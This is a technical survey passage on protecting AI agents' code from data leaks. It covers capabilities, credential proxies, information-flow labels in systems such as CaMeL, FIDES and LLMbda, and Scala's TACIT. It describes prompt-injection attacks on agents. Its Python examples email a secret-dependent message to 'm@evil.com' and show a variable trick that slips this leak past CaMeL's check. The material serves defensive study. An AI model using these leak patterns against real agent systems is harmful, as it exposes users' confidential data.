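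Someone who obtains a reference to the contracts folder can read next month's contracts, which someone who has only learned the contents of one contract cannot do. In a system that keeps capabilities apart from data, leaking information does not give the recipient a reference. Suppose that the contracts program sends an outsider, bit by bit, the number that its runtime uses internally to identify the folder. The outsider cannot use the number to reach the folder, because they have no operation that turns it back into a reference.

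The program could still read documents for the outsider and send back their contents. *Re: confinement with endogenous verification* (Brunswick, 2005) quotes a message in which Shapiro pointed out that this access ends once somebody kills the program that holds the capability. Shapiro added that a covert channel lets a program disclose information but doesn't let an outsider steal it, because the sender has to take part. Brunswick doubted that this distinction meant much when a bug such as a buffer overflow could cause a program to disclose information, and Shapiro shared the concern. The doubt applies at least as strongly to agent code, since instructions hidden in a document may be enough to make an agent write a program that leaks.

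The protection disappears when knowing a string is enough to gain access. Shapiro's example is Amoeba, a distributed operating system in which a capability was a record containing a server's address, an object number, a set of permitted operations and a large random number. Its designer, Andrew Tanenbaum, had asked how hard it would be for a program to guess such a record. According to Shapiro, Tanenbaum had not considered that an authorised program might deliberately give one away, or that a hostile developer might hide one in a program before anyone runs it. The random number does not prevent either. A program can also compress or disguise the record, so a monitor may not recognise it.

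Miller and colleagues mention two systems of this type whose designers worked around the problem. But in a later message, Shapiro describes the whole approach as impossible to secure.

API keys work in the same way as Amoeba's records, and so do secret web addresses, such as a link that opens a document for anyone who has it. If the contracts program can read the key to the status service, it can hide the key in a status message. Anyone who extracts the key can post messages until somebody cancels it, even after the program has ended.

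### Keeping credentials outside the sandbox

Agent code should be able to use a credential without having access to the credential itself. In an object-capability runtime, the operator can store the key in the private state of the status object, which adds the key to each outgoing request. The contracts program can call the object but cannot read its state. If agent code makes ordinary network requests from a sandbox, a proxy outside the sandbox needs to add the key.

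Deno Sandbox, a hosted product introduced in February 2026, is one example. The operator registers each secret and the hosts that may receive it. According to Willison, the variable that would normally hold the key inside the sandbox holds a placeholder instead. Outgoing requests pass through a proxy, which replaces the placeholder with the real key only if the request is going to an approved host. A program that leaks the variable therefore leaks only the placeholder. Anthropic gives the reason for this pattern: "if credentials never enter the sandbox, they can't be exfiltrated". Tokenizer, a project from the hosting company Fly, follows the same pattern.

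Such a proxy is compatible with Shapiro's objection to capabilities made of data. He thought it harmful to let an application see the secret bits, but saw no harm in exposing them within the trusted part of a system or between two trusted parts over an encrypted connection.

The arrangement still leaves the operator some work:

- The program can use the key through the proxy for as long as it runs, so the key itself should permit only what the task requires.
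- A service that repeats the key in its replies or error messages would hand it to the program. The proxy has to remove it from those as well.
- To fix the recipient as well as the host, the proxy should attach the operator's own credential to every request and refuse requests that arrive with a different one. This would address the weakness in the file-upload case.
- The proxy protects only the credentials that the operator knows about, and not, for instance, a supplier's password in one of the contracts.

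None of this stops the program from sending contract clauses to the status service in properly authorised requests. To prevent that, the operator has to separate the grants.

### Splitting the contracts program

The operator can ask the agent for two programs instead of one. The reading program summarises the contracts, and the reporting program communicates with the outside world.

| Grant | Reading program | Reporting program |
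|---|---|---|
| Contracts folder | Read | None |
| Summary file | Write | None |
| Status service | None | Post messages and receive replies |
| One-way channel | Read | Write |

The conversion service is hard to assign to either program. The reading program needs the converted text, but the service belongs to another company and shows job names to its other users. The operator's own code can send the whole folder to the service before either program starts, using numbers as job names, so that nothing the agent code reads can influence what the service receives. The company still sees every contract, though, and the operator pays for pages that the reading program may never use.

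With this arrangement, the reading program cannot post contract text to the status service, either by mistake or because a contract contains hidden instructions to do so. Even a hostile reporting program has no contract text to reveal. The operator does not have to inspect either program. The extra start-up time is small in a light sandbox. *Sandlock*, which can run each stage of a task under its own restrictions, adds about five milliseconds per start.

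The guarantee depends on the direction of the channel. In one of *Sandlock*'s examples, a stage that can read a private file pipes its contents to a stage that cannot open the file. This is safe because the later stage has no network access either. If it had, it could send out the secret it received, because *Sandlock* restricts what each stage can reach but not what passes through the pipe. In the contracts example, data must therefore flow only from the reporting program to the reading program. The two programs must also share no scratch folder or package cache, and only staff who may see the contracts should be able to open the summary file.

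Data that flows in the permitted direction can still cause problems. The reporting program can pass on replies to a status message, such as a request for a shorter summary. A reply might also contain text designed to make the summary misleading. The split prevents the reading program from sending contracts to the person who wrote that text, but staff could still rely on a false summary.

The split makes the status messages much less useful. The operator's launcher can notify the reporting program that a job has started, because nobody has opened a contract by then. The reporting program cannot report that 40 of 120 contracts are finished or that a particular document failed to open. Even a message that the job has ended reveals something about the contracts, since the length of the run depends on them.

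Other tasks can no longer be done in the usual way. The reading program cannot look up a company in a public register, because the query would reveal the company's name. If the register is small enough, the operator can download all of it in advance and let the reading program search the copy. Agent code has no similar workaround for emailing a supplier about an unusual clause, because the message has to contain something from the contract.

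*Sandlock* acknowledges that a legitimate step in an agent's work often needs private data, outside communication and exposure to untrusted text together, and it leaves whoever writes the task to find a workable division. When one program has to hold both a confidential contract and an email connection, the runtime needs labels to track where each piece of data came from.

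## Labelling data and checking flows at run time

Information-flow control lets a program hold both a confidential contract and an email connection. The runtime attaches a label to every value, recording who may read it and whether an outsider could have written it. Anything the program computes from the value inherits the label. Each time the program tries to send something out, the runtime checks the labels against a policy.

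### How labels combine

Labels have an order, written ⊑ and read as "may flow to". The simplest scheme has two labels, public and secret, with public ⊑ secret, so a program may copy public data into a secret file but not secret data into a public one. Any two labels have a join, written ⊔, which is the least restrictive label that both may flow to. If a program pastes a secret clause under a public heading, the result gets the join of the two labels, which is secret. Dorothy Denning set out this approach in 1976 and called such a set of labels a "lattice", a term from mathematics.

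Two labels are too few for the contracts program if its summary has several groups of readers. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) also describes labels that list everyone who may read a value. The join of two such lists is their intersection. If the legal and sales teams may read one contract, and legal and finance may read another, only legal may read a sentence that draws on both. Before a value goes to an output, the runtime checks that everyone who can read that output is on the value's list.

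Every value carries a secrecy label, which keeps it from the wrong readers, and a separate trust label, which keeps outsiders from influencing decisions such as which account receives a payment. Trust labels are ordered trusted ⊑ untrusted, so a result is untrusted if any of its inputs is. A supplier's contract is secret and untrusted, a news article is public and untrusted, and the operator's own price list is secret and trusted.

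Costa and colleagues give a rule for each label. If an action has serious consequences, both its arguments and the decision to take it must be trusted. If an action sends information out, everyone who can read the destination must be allowed to read the content. This secrecy rule alone does not stop prompt injection, in which an attacker hides instructions in data the agent reads. The attacker could still make the agent send a misleading message, but only with content the recipients are allowed to read.

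### Noninterference

The ideal is noninterference, which means that changing the secrets changes nothing an outside observer can see. To state this formally, choose a label *n* for the observer, who can see every value whose label may flow to *n*. Write *s₁* ~ₙ *s₂* if two starting states look the same to that observer, and *P(s)* for the final state when program *P* starts from *s*. The program is noninterfering at *n* if, for all starting states,

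*s₁* ~ₙ *s₂* implies *P(s₁)* ~ₙ *P(s₂)*.

For readers of the status service, *s₁* and *s₂* might contain entirely different contracts, but the status messages would have to be identical. If *n* is "trusted", the same formula requires that an attacker who changes the untrusted inputs cannot change any trusted result.

Enforcement at run time usually achieves a weaker property, termination-insensitive noninterference, which requires *P(s₁)* ~ₙ *P(s₂)* only when both runs finish. The property must be weaker because a monitor prevents leaks by stopping programs, and whether it stops one may depend on a secret. Someone who learns that a run failed can therefore learn something about the secret, and repeated runs can reveal more.

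A language model can give different replies to the same prompt, so Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) compare probability distributions in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*. Let *μ₁* and *μ₂* be the distributions of what the observer sees from the two starting states. Each may sum to less than 1, and the remainder is the probability that the run never finishes. The definition requires a third distribution *ω*, also summing to at most 1, that is at least as large as both *μ₁* and *μ₂* for every outcome.

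If all runs finish, this makes *μ₁* and *μ₂* equal. Otherwise, the statistical distance between them, which is half the sum of their absolute differences over all outcomes, is at most the average of the two probabilities of not finishing. For example, if 2% of runs fail to finish with one set of contracts and 4% with another, the distance is at most 0.03.

### Explicit and implicit flows

A flow is explicit if the program copies or transforms the data, for example by pasting a clause into a message. It is implicit if the data affects which instructions run. In an example from Garby and colleagues, a hidden instruction tries to reveal something about a customer's balance:

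```python
if account.balance > threshold:
    send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

The email contains only fixed text, so checking only the text's label would allow it. To catch this leak, the runtime also keeps a program-counter label, which tracks the program's control flow. When the program branches on a secret, this label becomes secret and applies to everything the program does inside the branch. CaMeL, an agent system that Edoardo Debenedetti and colleagues presented in 2025, tracks control flow this way and blocks the email.

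Garby and colleagues found that an attacker can get around CaMeL's check with a couple of extra variables. Their attack works like this:

```python
tmp = True
rich = True
if account.balance > threshold:
    tmp = False
if tmp:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

CaMeL raises a variable's label only on the branch that the program takes. The two possible runs then go as follows:

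| Step | Balance above the threshold | Balance at or below the threshold |
|---|---|---|
| Set both variables | Both true and public | Both true and public |
| Test the balance | `tmp` becomes false and secret | Branch skipped, `tmp` stays true and public |
| Test `tmp` | Branch skipped, `rich` stays true and public | `rich` becomes false and stays public |
| Test `rich` | Program sends the email | Program sends nothing |

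The attacker receives an email exactly when the balance exceeds the threshold, yet `rich` is public in both runs. In the run that sends the email, the secret affects `rich` by preventing an assignment. A purely dynamic monitor changes labels only when an instruction runs, so it does not mark `rich` as secret when the assignment is skipped. The monitor follows only one of the two runs that noninterference compares. J. S. Fenton described this problem in 1974.

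The "no high upgrade" rule, from Thomas Austin and Cormac Flanagan, prevents this leak. It forbids a program from assigning to a public variable while its control flow depends on secret data. If the balance is above the threshold, the assignment `tmp = False` breaks the rule and the runtime stops the program. If the balance is lower, the program runs to the end. The attacker gets no email in either case, but anyone who can tell that the runtime stopped the program still learns that the balance is above the threshold.

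A programmer can avoid the stop by marking both variables secret from the beginning. The assignments are then allowed, but the test of `rich` is secret too, so the runtime blocks any email that depends on it.

Another solution is to examine both branches before the program runs. In *SPA* (Girrens and Wang, 2026), a model writes a complete plan in a restricted language. A checker follows labels through the plan's data and branches, and rejects unsafe plans before they call any tools. A type system can check ordinary code in a similar way.

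### CaMeL and FIDES

Models make labels harder to track. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) points out that a conventional runtime can label each variable, but a model processes its whole conversation as one stream of tokens, which may mix several sources. Both CaMeL and Microsoft's FIDES (Costa et al.) try to keep restricted text away from the model that plans the work.

CaMeL uses two models. The planning model turns the user's request into a Python program, and a custom interpreter runs it. The quarantined model, which cannot call tools, reads untrusted text and returns values to the program. The planning model does not read those values.

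According to Girrens and Wang, each value in CaMeL carries a record of where it came from and who may receive it. CaMeL's designers call these records capabilities, but they are labels, since holding one gives no right to use anything. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) explains that the interpreter also records which values each result depends on. The interpreter checks a policy at every tool call. A summary from the quarantined model therefore remains subject to restrictions on the text it summarises.

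CaMeL's designers considered implicit flows. *PolicySniff* (2026) describes CaMeL's strict mode, which tracks dependencies created by conditions and exceptions, and notes that the interpreter offers no clock, which rules out a timing attack the designers discuss. The example with `rich` shows that this tracking is incomplete. Garby and colleagues also found that inserting an untrusted value into fixed text made the value trusted. When a program fails, CaMeL retries in an ordinary Python loop outside the interpreter, so the new attempt starts without the old labels. CaMeL censors the error messages to reduce the resulting leak, but there is no proof that this is enough. Its designers offer no general soundness theorem and call formalisation a "crucial direction" for further work.

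In FIDES, the planning model chooses one tool call at a time and may see the results before choosing the next. Messages, tool arguments and tool results carry labels for secrecy and trust. Everything the model writes gets the join of the labels in its conversation, so reading a single untrusted email would make all its later decisions untrusted.

To prevent this, FIDES puts a result in a variable if its label is more restrictive than the conversation's, and shows the model only the variable's name. If a user asks for a summary of three emails in a Slack message, FIDES can proceed in three steps:

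1. The planning model calls the email tool, and FIDES stores the emails in a variable.
2. The planning model asks a separate model without tools to summarise that variable. The summary goes into a second variable with the emails' labels.
3. The planning model calls the messaging tool with the recipient named by the user and the name of the second variable. FIDES inserts the summary just before the call.

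A policy can allow untrusted text to be sent to a trusted recipient. If the next step depends on what an email contains, the planning model can either open the variable holding the email and take on the variable's label, or request an answer in a fixed format that limits what comes back.

Costa and colleagues prove a property called explicit secrecy, which means that any given sequence of tool calls has the same visible effects from two starting states that look the same to an outsider. The property does not compare different sequences, so an agent may still reveal a secret by choosing between two harmless-looking messages. The proof treats the model as deterministic and does not cover timing or the size of network packets.

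This omission is deliberate. Costa and colleagues argue that full noninterference would in practice forbid almost every public action after the agent had read a secret. Leaving it out is a reasonable compromise for an agent that makes a few dozen tool calls, but a poor one for agent code, which can branch on a secret thousands of times a second. Garby and colleagues make a related objection, that the guarantee is weakest where data can become code.

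### The LLMbda calculus

Garby and colleagues built LLMbda, a small programming language for agents in which every value has a label. Each conversation with a model also has a label, the join of the labels of all messages sent so far. The runtime runs the model's replies as code, with a program-counter label at least as restrictive as the conversation's. Code from a model that has read a secret contract therefore cannot produce a public result.

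A program can keep a conversation public by forking it, letting the model read the contract in the copy, and then returning to the original. The rule against high upgrades also applies to conversations. In one example, a program asks the model to remember that `x` is false. If a secret is true, the program then tells the model to set `x` to true. The runtime blocks this second message because the public conversation would otherwise reveal whether the program had sent it.

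Garby and colleagues prove a probabilistic form of termination-insensitive noninterference for every program in the language, including programs that generate and run new code. The result holds whatever a hostile reply contains. The proof checker Lean verified the proof, and the interpreter in the proof is the same one that calls the model.

The theorem does not rule out leaks through whether a program terminates or how long it takes to produce its results. It also assumes that all data sources are part of the program. With real tools, the operator has to label incoming data correctly and put a check on every sensitive tool.

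LLMbda's `endorse` instruction relabels an untrusted value as trusted. A program might need it to pay a bill, since the amount comes from a document that somebody else wrote. Endorsing the wrong value can let an attacker choose the payee, but Garby and colleagues prove that no use of `endorse` can make a secret public.

### ChainCaps

*ChainCaps* (Jiang, Yang and colleagues, 2026) places the tracking in a proxy between the agent and its tools, so neither has to change. Each value carries a list, called a budget, of the destinations it may still reach, such as one folder or the pages under one web address. When a tool combines several values, the result keeps only the destinations that every input and the tool's own description allow. For example, if a salary sheet may appear only on the user's screen, a summary combining it with public news may also appear there, but the agent cannot email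 that summary.

When a model reads several values, the proxy cannot determine which of them influenced its next output. It therefore keeps one list of permitted destinations for the whole conversation, and narrows it each time the model reads something with fewer permitted destinations. The proxy applies the narrowed list to everything the model writes afterwards.

Jiang and colleagues prove that if the ChainCaps proxy allows a call without an explicit release, every source that contributed to the call's arguments permitted the call's destination from the start. They assume that the tool descriptions are correct and that the proxy observes the relevant data flows. ChainCaps does not track covert channels, implicit flows through a model's hidden state, or operating system effects that bypass the proxy.

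ChainCaps was tested on 56 attacks and 26 ordinary tasks, using five models and three runs of each task. It reduced the attack success rate from between 25.2% and 67.8%, depending on the model, to between 0% and 4.8%, and the agents still completed at least 96% of ordinary tasks. Some of the attacks that still succeeded wrote a script for later execution or passed data between shell commands, where the proxy could not track it. This is a serious limitation for agent code because the code can do all its work between two tool calls.

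In a separate test, ChainCaps blocked 100% of attacks with tool descriptions written by experts, 90.9% with descriptions written from a checklist, and 27.3% with naive ones. The naive descriptions also prevented half of the ordinary tasks from finishing.

Jiang and colleagues also replayed recorded attacks against a simplified version of FIDES. ChainCaps blocked 59.5% of the attacks from GPT-5.1 runs, and the simplified FIDES blocked 16.1%. But the simplified version gave each value a level on a single scale, whereas FIDES can also use lists of readers. The result is therefore better evidence that detailed labels help than that ChainCaps outperforms FIDES.

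### What enforcement costs

Most other evaluations use AgentDojo, a benchmark of simulated office work, travel booking, banking and Slack messaging. An agent attempts ordinary tasks, with or without malicious instructions in the data it reads. The benchmark measures how many tasks the agent completes (its utility) and how many attacks succeed.

Garby and colleagues tested an LLMbda agent called Randori on the banking tasks. They combined 16 tasks with nine attacks and ran each of the 144 pairs three times on each of three models, for 1,296 attacked runs. Attacks succeeded in two runs, both of the same pair on GPT-5.2. The user had asked the agent to read a file and pay the bill it described, but the attacker had replaced the file with a false bill, and the agent endorsed its contents. Without `endorse`, the runtime blocks this attack, but it also prevents the agent from paying a genuine bill.

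The total makes the result look stronger than it is, because only 47 of the 144 pairs tested the labels. In the other 97, the attack needed a tool that the agent's plan would never call, so fixing the plan in advance was generally enough to stop it. A perfect score on the 47 pairs would be consistent with a true resistance rate as low as 92.4%, the lower bound of the 95% confidence interval that Garby and colleagues give.

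They also ran CaMeL on the banking tasks with two of the models, with and without its policy checks. The checks roughly halved CaMeL's utility. Five attacks succeeded in 622 completed runs without the checks, and none succeeded in 588 with them. These figures may understate how much protection the checks provide, because the benchmark's attacks do not adapt to the defence.

Other systems show losses of various sizes:

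| System | AgentDojo tasks | Utility, checks off | Utility, checks on | Reported by |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| CaMeL with GPT-5.2 | Banking | 66.7% | 37.5% | Garby and colleagues |
| CaMeL with MiMo-v2.5 | Banking | 70.8% | 37.5% | Garby and colleagues |
| TypeGuard, a Haskell system | Slack | 71.4% | 38.1% | Garby and colleagues |
| FIDES with GPT-4o | Office work | 63.5% | 59.0% | Costa and colleagues |
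| FIDES with GPT-4o | Travel | 50.0% | 41.0% | Costa and colleagues |
| FIDES with GPT-4o | Banking | 65.0% | 52.5% | Costa and colleagues |
| FIDES with GPT-4o | Slack | 63.8% | 47.6% | Costa and colleagues |
| SPA | All, one request at a time | 53.0% | 29.0% | Girrens and Wang |

Randori completed 75% of the banking tasks with GPT-5.2 while enforcing its labels. The comparison with CaMeL is uneven, because Randori implements only some of CaMeL's policies and can endorse data. When Garby and colleagues removed `endorse`, Randori completed 54.2% of the tasks with MiMo-v2.5, still more than CaMeL's 37.5%. Because there were only 16 different tasks, the margins of error on these three figures range from about ±19 to ±27 percentage points.

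CaMeL's designers reported a much smaller drop in completed tasks. According to *Where Agent Defenses Fail* (2026), they found that CaMeL solved 77% of AgentDojo tasks, compared with 84% for an undefended agent. The drop may be smaller partly because they tested more than the banking tasks. Banking is an unusually hard case because many of its tasks tell the agent to read an untrusted file and act on it.

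For FIDES, the table understates the total drop in task completion, because hiding data in variables also makes tasks harder for the model. With GPT-4o, a simple agent with no protection completed 98.8% of the banking tasks, compared with 65.0% for FIDES before any policy checks. With o1, a stronger reasoning model, hiding data reduced task completion by only 6.3% on average across all tasks.

In the test, 152 attacks succeeded against the simple agent and none against FIDES with policy checks, after Costa and colleagues discounted three that AgentDojo counted as successes. Two design choices limit what can be concluded from this result. Costa and colleagues marked a data field as untrusted if at least one of the benchmark's attacks used it, so the labels were fitted to the attacks in advance. They also chose which data to hide based only on whether it was untrusted, not on whether it was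 secret. The test is therefore weak evidence of how well an agent would work while protecting confidential contracts.

Some of the lost utility is unavoidable. Any policy that keeps outsiders from directing payments will block a task that asks an agent to follow whatever instructions a file contains. Other losses come from labels that are more restrictive than the data requires.

### Over-labelling

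Over-labelling, also called label creep, occurs because joins can only make labels more restrictive. Suppose an agent reads a confidential contract and then writes a message saying that the office closes at five. The message gets the contract's label because both were in the same conversation, so the runtime refuses to post the message publicly. After enough work, the agent may be unable to send anything to anyone.

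Gregory, Domico and colleagues (2026), in *The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems*, simulated how labels spread through groups of agents, without using language models. They divided tasks of 20 tool calls among 5 to 20 agents and counted the calls that introduced or carried a sensitive label. The count was lower when agents could communicate directly instead of passing messages through others, and when the sensitive tools belonged to a few dedicated agents. Using more agents also lowered the count, but the number of connections to monitor could grow with the square of the number of agents. Even in the best arrangement, many calls still had a sensitive label, so Gregory and colleagues concluded that systems also need a way to remove labels.

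Separate conversations keep labels apart, just as splitting the contracts program into parts with separate grants would keep secrets and outputs apart. *Language-Based Agent Control* (2026) applies this separation within a single agent. A sub-agent reads the restricted text and returns a labelled result, and the main agent's label rises only if the main agent opens that result. Unlike CaMeL's quarantined model, the sub-agent can call tools, within the limits of its labels.

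Other systems estimate which inputs actually affected a model's output. *Sightline* (2026) removed half of the unnecessary labels in one experiment, but missed a real flow in 3.9% of episodes. *Ghost in the Agent* (2026) compared a similar tracker, NeuroTaint, with FIDES on 400 scenarios. FIDES reported a flow in 94 of 140 scenarios that had none, while NeuroTaint did so in only one. FIDES also missed 23 of 40 implicit flows, and NeuroTaint missed three. However, NeuroTaint gave a false alarm in all 14 scenarios where several sources covered overlapping subjects, which would happen constantly with a folder of similar contracts.

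Estimates like these lack the guarantee of a conservative join, which may block a harmless message but never loses a label. A tracker that misses 3.9% of cases might be adequate against accidental leaks, but an attacker can keep looking for those cases.

A more precise policy can also reduce needless refusals without guesswork. In *LLM Agent Capabilities Should Follow Task Intent and Context Source*, Zheng, Zhang and Mao (2026) set rules for each field of a tool call. When their agent extracts tables from a PDF and reports them in a software project, the rules allow text from the PDF to fill the body of the report, but only the user's request can determine which project receives it.

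*Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (Shim, Karim and colleagues, 2026) describes FlowSeal, a system that allows labels to be removed under supervision. FlowSeal intercepts every attempt to write or share data. When necessary, it has a model outside the agent's conversation judge whether the proposed text reveals any protected record, so the decision to release the text depends on that model's judgement. Across the paper's tests, FlowSeal leaked at most 3.3% of protected items and completed 72.4% of ordinary tasks, close to the 75.9% completed by the best alternative.

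### Labels in the contracts program

To use labels, the operator first replaces the contracts folder with an object that returns labelled documents. Suppose the legal team may read every contract, sales may also read the one with Acme, and finance the one with Birch. Outsiders wrote parts of both, so both are untrusted. The operator decides that the number of contracts is public. The program might then look like this:

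```js
let done = 0;
let flagged = 0;
for (const contract of folder.list()) {
  const section = summarise(contract);
  summary.append(section);
  done += 1;
  status.post(`${done} contracts finished`);
  if (section.includes('penalty')) flagged += 1;
}
```

If `summarise` starts a new conversation with a model for each contract, the sections on Acme and Birch each keep the same permitted readers as the contract they summarise. If it uses one conversation for everything, only the legal team may read any section written after the model has seen both contracts. The summary file must also store a label with each section and show readers only the sections they may see. Neither section could be written to an ordinary file open to all three teams.

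The status message is now allowed because its text depends only on `done`, which the program increases once per contract, whatever the contract contains. The split program in the previous arrangement could not report progress at all. Labels do not hide when each message appears, however, and a long contract will still delay the next message.

The last line of the loop mistakenly changes the public variable `flagged` after a test on secret text, so the runtime stops the program at the first contract that mentions a penalty. If the messages end at "17 contracts finished", anyone reading them can infer that the seventeenth contract mentions one. The termination channel has then leaked nearly seven bits by revealing which of the 120 contracts is the first to mention a penalty. The programmer can prevent the stop by giving `flagged` the legal team's label from the start. The count may then go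 into the legal team's part of the summary but never into a status message. A trial run on invented contracts would expose the error before any real data leaked, much as Randori practises on an artificial bank account before using the real one.

Labels also let the program email a supplier about an unusual clause. Once the operator adds Acme to the readers of Acme's contract, the program can send Acme text from that contract, but the runtime refuses any message that also draws on Birch's contract. The email's body may be untrusted, but its address must come from the operator's trusted list of suppliers. An instruction hidden in a contract could therefore distort the email's wording but not change where it is sent.

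The conversion company must be listed as a reader of every document it receives. Its replies arrive without labels, so the object that gives the program access to the company has to attach the original document's label to the converted text. If it doesn't, the program can post the converted contract publicly without breaking any rule.

Labelling data and checking flows this way requires a runtime that tracks values inside the program, as the CaMeL and LLMbda interpreters do. If the operator runs ordinary JavaScript behind a proxy, the proxy cannot distinguish `done` from `flagged`. To be safe, it would have to give every output the labels of everything the program had read, and the progress messages would stop after the first contract.

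## Keeping secrets inside functions that have no effects

Labels require a runtime that tracks every value. A compiler can do much of this work before the program runs by checking which capabilities each piece of code can use. If only code with no capabilities may read a contract's text, that code can compute with the text but cannot send it anywhere.

*Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) applies this idea in a system called TACIT, short for Tracked Agent Capabilities In Types. The agent writes programs in Scala 3, and TACIT runs only those that pass the compiler's checks. In one example, an agent summarises changes in confidential contracts. The paper assumes that the model writing the code may be hostile and that it runs on another company's servers, so the contract text must be kept from the model too. A sandbox alone can't ensure this, because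 the agent needs both to read files and to contact its model.

### Capture sets

Scala 3 has an experimental feature called capture checking, which adds a capture set to a value's type, listing the capabilities that the value may hold. *What's in the Box* (Xu, Bračevac and colleagues, 2025) gives the example of a logger that writes to a file `f` and to the console, and so has the type `Logger^{f, console}`. A function that calls the logger has the logger in its own capture set, which shows that the function can also reach the file and the console. A capture set must include every capability that the value uses, but it may also include some that the value never uses.

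Function types use different arrows to show what a function may capture:

| Type | Capabilities the function may use |
|---|---|
| `A => B` | Any |
| `A ->{f} B` | Only `f`, or capabilities derived from it |
| `A -> B` | None |

Functions of the last type are called pure. A programmer can require one computation to be pure and still let the rest of the program read files and send messages.

Object-capability languages normally forbid global objects that give access to the outside world, since any code could use them. Scala can permit them because a function that uses one, such as a global console, has that object in its capture set and so cannot count as pure.

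### The Classified wrapper

TACIT returns the contents of protected files in a wrapper called `Classified`. In the contracts example, Odersky and colleagues give it three methods. The agent does most of its work with `map`, which applies a function to the contents and wraps the result:

```scala
def map[U](f: T -> U): Classified[U]
```

Here `T` is the type of the contents and `U` is the type of the function's result. The `aggregate` method combines two wrapped values into one. The `reveal` method returns the contents, but only to code with a `CanAccess` capability, which the agent does not have. Converting a wrapped value to text produces only `Classified(****)`.

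The arrow in `map` prevents the leak, because it accepts only pure functions. In one test, an agent tried to write confidential security recommendations to a file:

```scala
classifiedRecs.map { content =>
  outFile.write(content)
}
```

This function captures `outFile`, so its type is `String ->{outFile} Unit`. The compiler rejected the program because the `map` method requires `String -> Unit`. The agent may have meant no harm, since the file was in the protected folder. TACIT has a separate method that takes the wrapped value and writes it only to protected files.

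The same rule stops implicit flows. In the attack on CaMeL, the program tests a secret balance and then changes an ordinary variable. In TACIT, a program can test the balance only inside a pure function passed to `map`, and that function cannot change a variable outside itself.

A run-time monitor can leak information by stopping a program after it has read a secret. The compiler rejects a program before the program opens any file, so the rejection reveals nothing about the files' contents and leaves no work half done. *LACUNA* (Zhao, Xu and colleagues, 2026), which describes a later system from the same research group, gives an example in which a model's code subtracts 50 from a balance of 100 and then returns text where the caller expects a number. The compiler rejects the whole program, so the balance remains 100.

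### The model that reads the contracts

The agent's own model is not allowed to read the contracts, so TACIT provides a `chat` function that sends wrapped text to a second model and wraps the reply. Like CaMeL's quarantined model, this second model has no tools.

The compiler treats `chat` as pure, although the call sends text to another service. The operator therefore has to make sure the service neither passes the text on nor uses it as context for later requests. According to the project's code repository, lampepfl's *TACIT*, the second model can run behind any OpenAI-compatible interface. The type check would pass even if the operator entered the address of the company the wrapper was supposed to keep out.

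When the program prints a summary, TACIT sends the text to the user's terminal and only `Classified(****)` to the agent's model. The summary stays wrapped in later turns. If the user asks how long the summary is, the agent can run `summary.map(_.length)` and print the result, and only the user sees the number. Text can lose its labels when it enters a model's conversation, but this design avoids that unless the user quotes the summary in the next message.

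### Capabilities that cannot outlive their block

A program obtains access to files by calling `requestFileSystem` with a folder and a block of code. The capability is valid only until the block returns. A program might try to keep it longer by returning a function that uses it:

```scala
val bad = requestFileSystem("/data"): fs =>
  () => fs.access("secret.txt").read()
```

The returned function has `fs` in its capture set, but the result type of `requestFileSystem` cannot refer to `fs`, so the compiler rejects the code. Santos-Grueiro's monitor rejects expired grants while the program runs, whereas this check prevents the program from starting. A wrapped document may leave the block because it is data and gives no access to the file system.

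TACIT's published interface has methods that let the program itself name the folder, web hosts and commands it will use. An operator who wants to make these choices has to restrict those methods in the library or supply ready-made objects, as Odersky and colleagues do in their contracts example.

### Turning exceptions into values

A pure function can still throw an exception. Division by zero and stack overflow can happen almost anywhere, and Scala's *Safe Mode*, the reference page for the restricted language, calls it too cumbersome to demand a capability for each such case. The compiler therefore accepts a function like this one:

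```scala
contract.map { text => throw Exception(text) }
```

If the exception ended the program, the error message could expose the whole contract to the agent's model, which reads error messages to correct its code. Even without the message, the failure itself could reveal something about the contract.

TACIT catches exceptions at run time with Scala's `Try`, which runs a piece of code and returns either its result or a failure value holding the exception. TACIT can put the failure value in a `Classified` wrapper, where it looks like any other wrapped result, and the program continues. This makes mistakes hard to find. In one set of tests, the agent's instructions warn that if the code throws an exception, the user will see an empty result and the agent will see no error. They tell the agent to return an explanation instead, such as "No matching file found".

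`Try` does not catch errors that Scala treats as fatal, such as running out of memory, so the operator needs another way to keep those from revealing a secret. Pham, Bračevac and colleagues (2026), in *Classifying Capabilities (Extended Version)*, also found that Scala had wrongly declared `Try` values pure, because reading the result of a failed one throws the stored exception again. They corrected this by sorting capabilities into kinds, so that the type of a `Try` keeps the control-flow capabilities of the code it ran and drops the rest.

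### Three required properties and the parts to trust

Odersky and colleagues require three properties of the language in which agents write:

- **Capability safety:** a program cannot forge a capability or hide the fact that it needs one.
- **Capability completeness:** capabilities control every effect that matters for safety, apart from those that the runtime can contain, such as exceptions.
- **Local purity:** types can limit a particular computation to certain capabilities, or to none.

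Ordinary Scala lacks capability safety because a type cast can make a function that uses a file look pure. Scala's safe mode forbids unchecked casts, reflection and other features that could remove capabilities from types. It also turns on capture checking, including for changes to variables, and allows global objects only if they are safe themselves. Mazur's *Scala 3.8.3 is now available!* introduces safe mode as an experimental feature and shows the compiler rejecting a cast and a direct call to `println`.

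Library authors can exempt their own code from these rules by marking it `@assumeSafe`, and they are then responsible for checking it. Scala's reference page gives the example of a cache that stores the results of earlier calls. The cache never changes a result, but a stored result arrives sooner, so a program that can read a clock might learn which values an earlier function had looked up.

The operator has to trust the compiler, TACIT's library, the runtime and the second model, if they use it. The library and its related tools total about 1,000 lines of Scala. In March 2026, lampepfl's documentation said that TACIT did not yet use the compiler's safe mode and instead searched programs for forbidden patterns. Such a search can miss patterns nobody thought to forbid. The documentation also recommends disabling the agent's built-in file, shell and network tools, because TACIT cannot check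 what the agent does with them.

More has been proved about the theory than about the software. Xu and colleagues used Lean to prove that a small model of capture checking is sound and that capabilities cannot escape their scope. Pham and colleagues did similar work for their extension. Odersky and colleagues acknowledge that nobody has yet proved that safe mode provides capability safety and local purity.

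The compiler can also have bugs. In *Capture leak when using varargs?*, a thread on Scala's user forum, a programmer reported that the checker had dropped some capabilities from a function's type. Someone confirmed the bug in a reply and added that the checker would even have accepted the function as pure. A bug like that could let `map` accept a function that sends its input out.

### How TACIT performed

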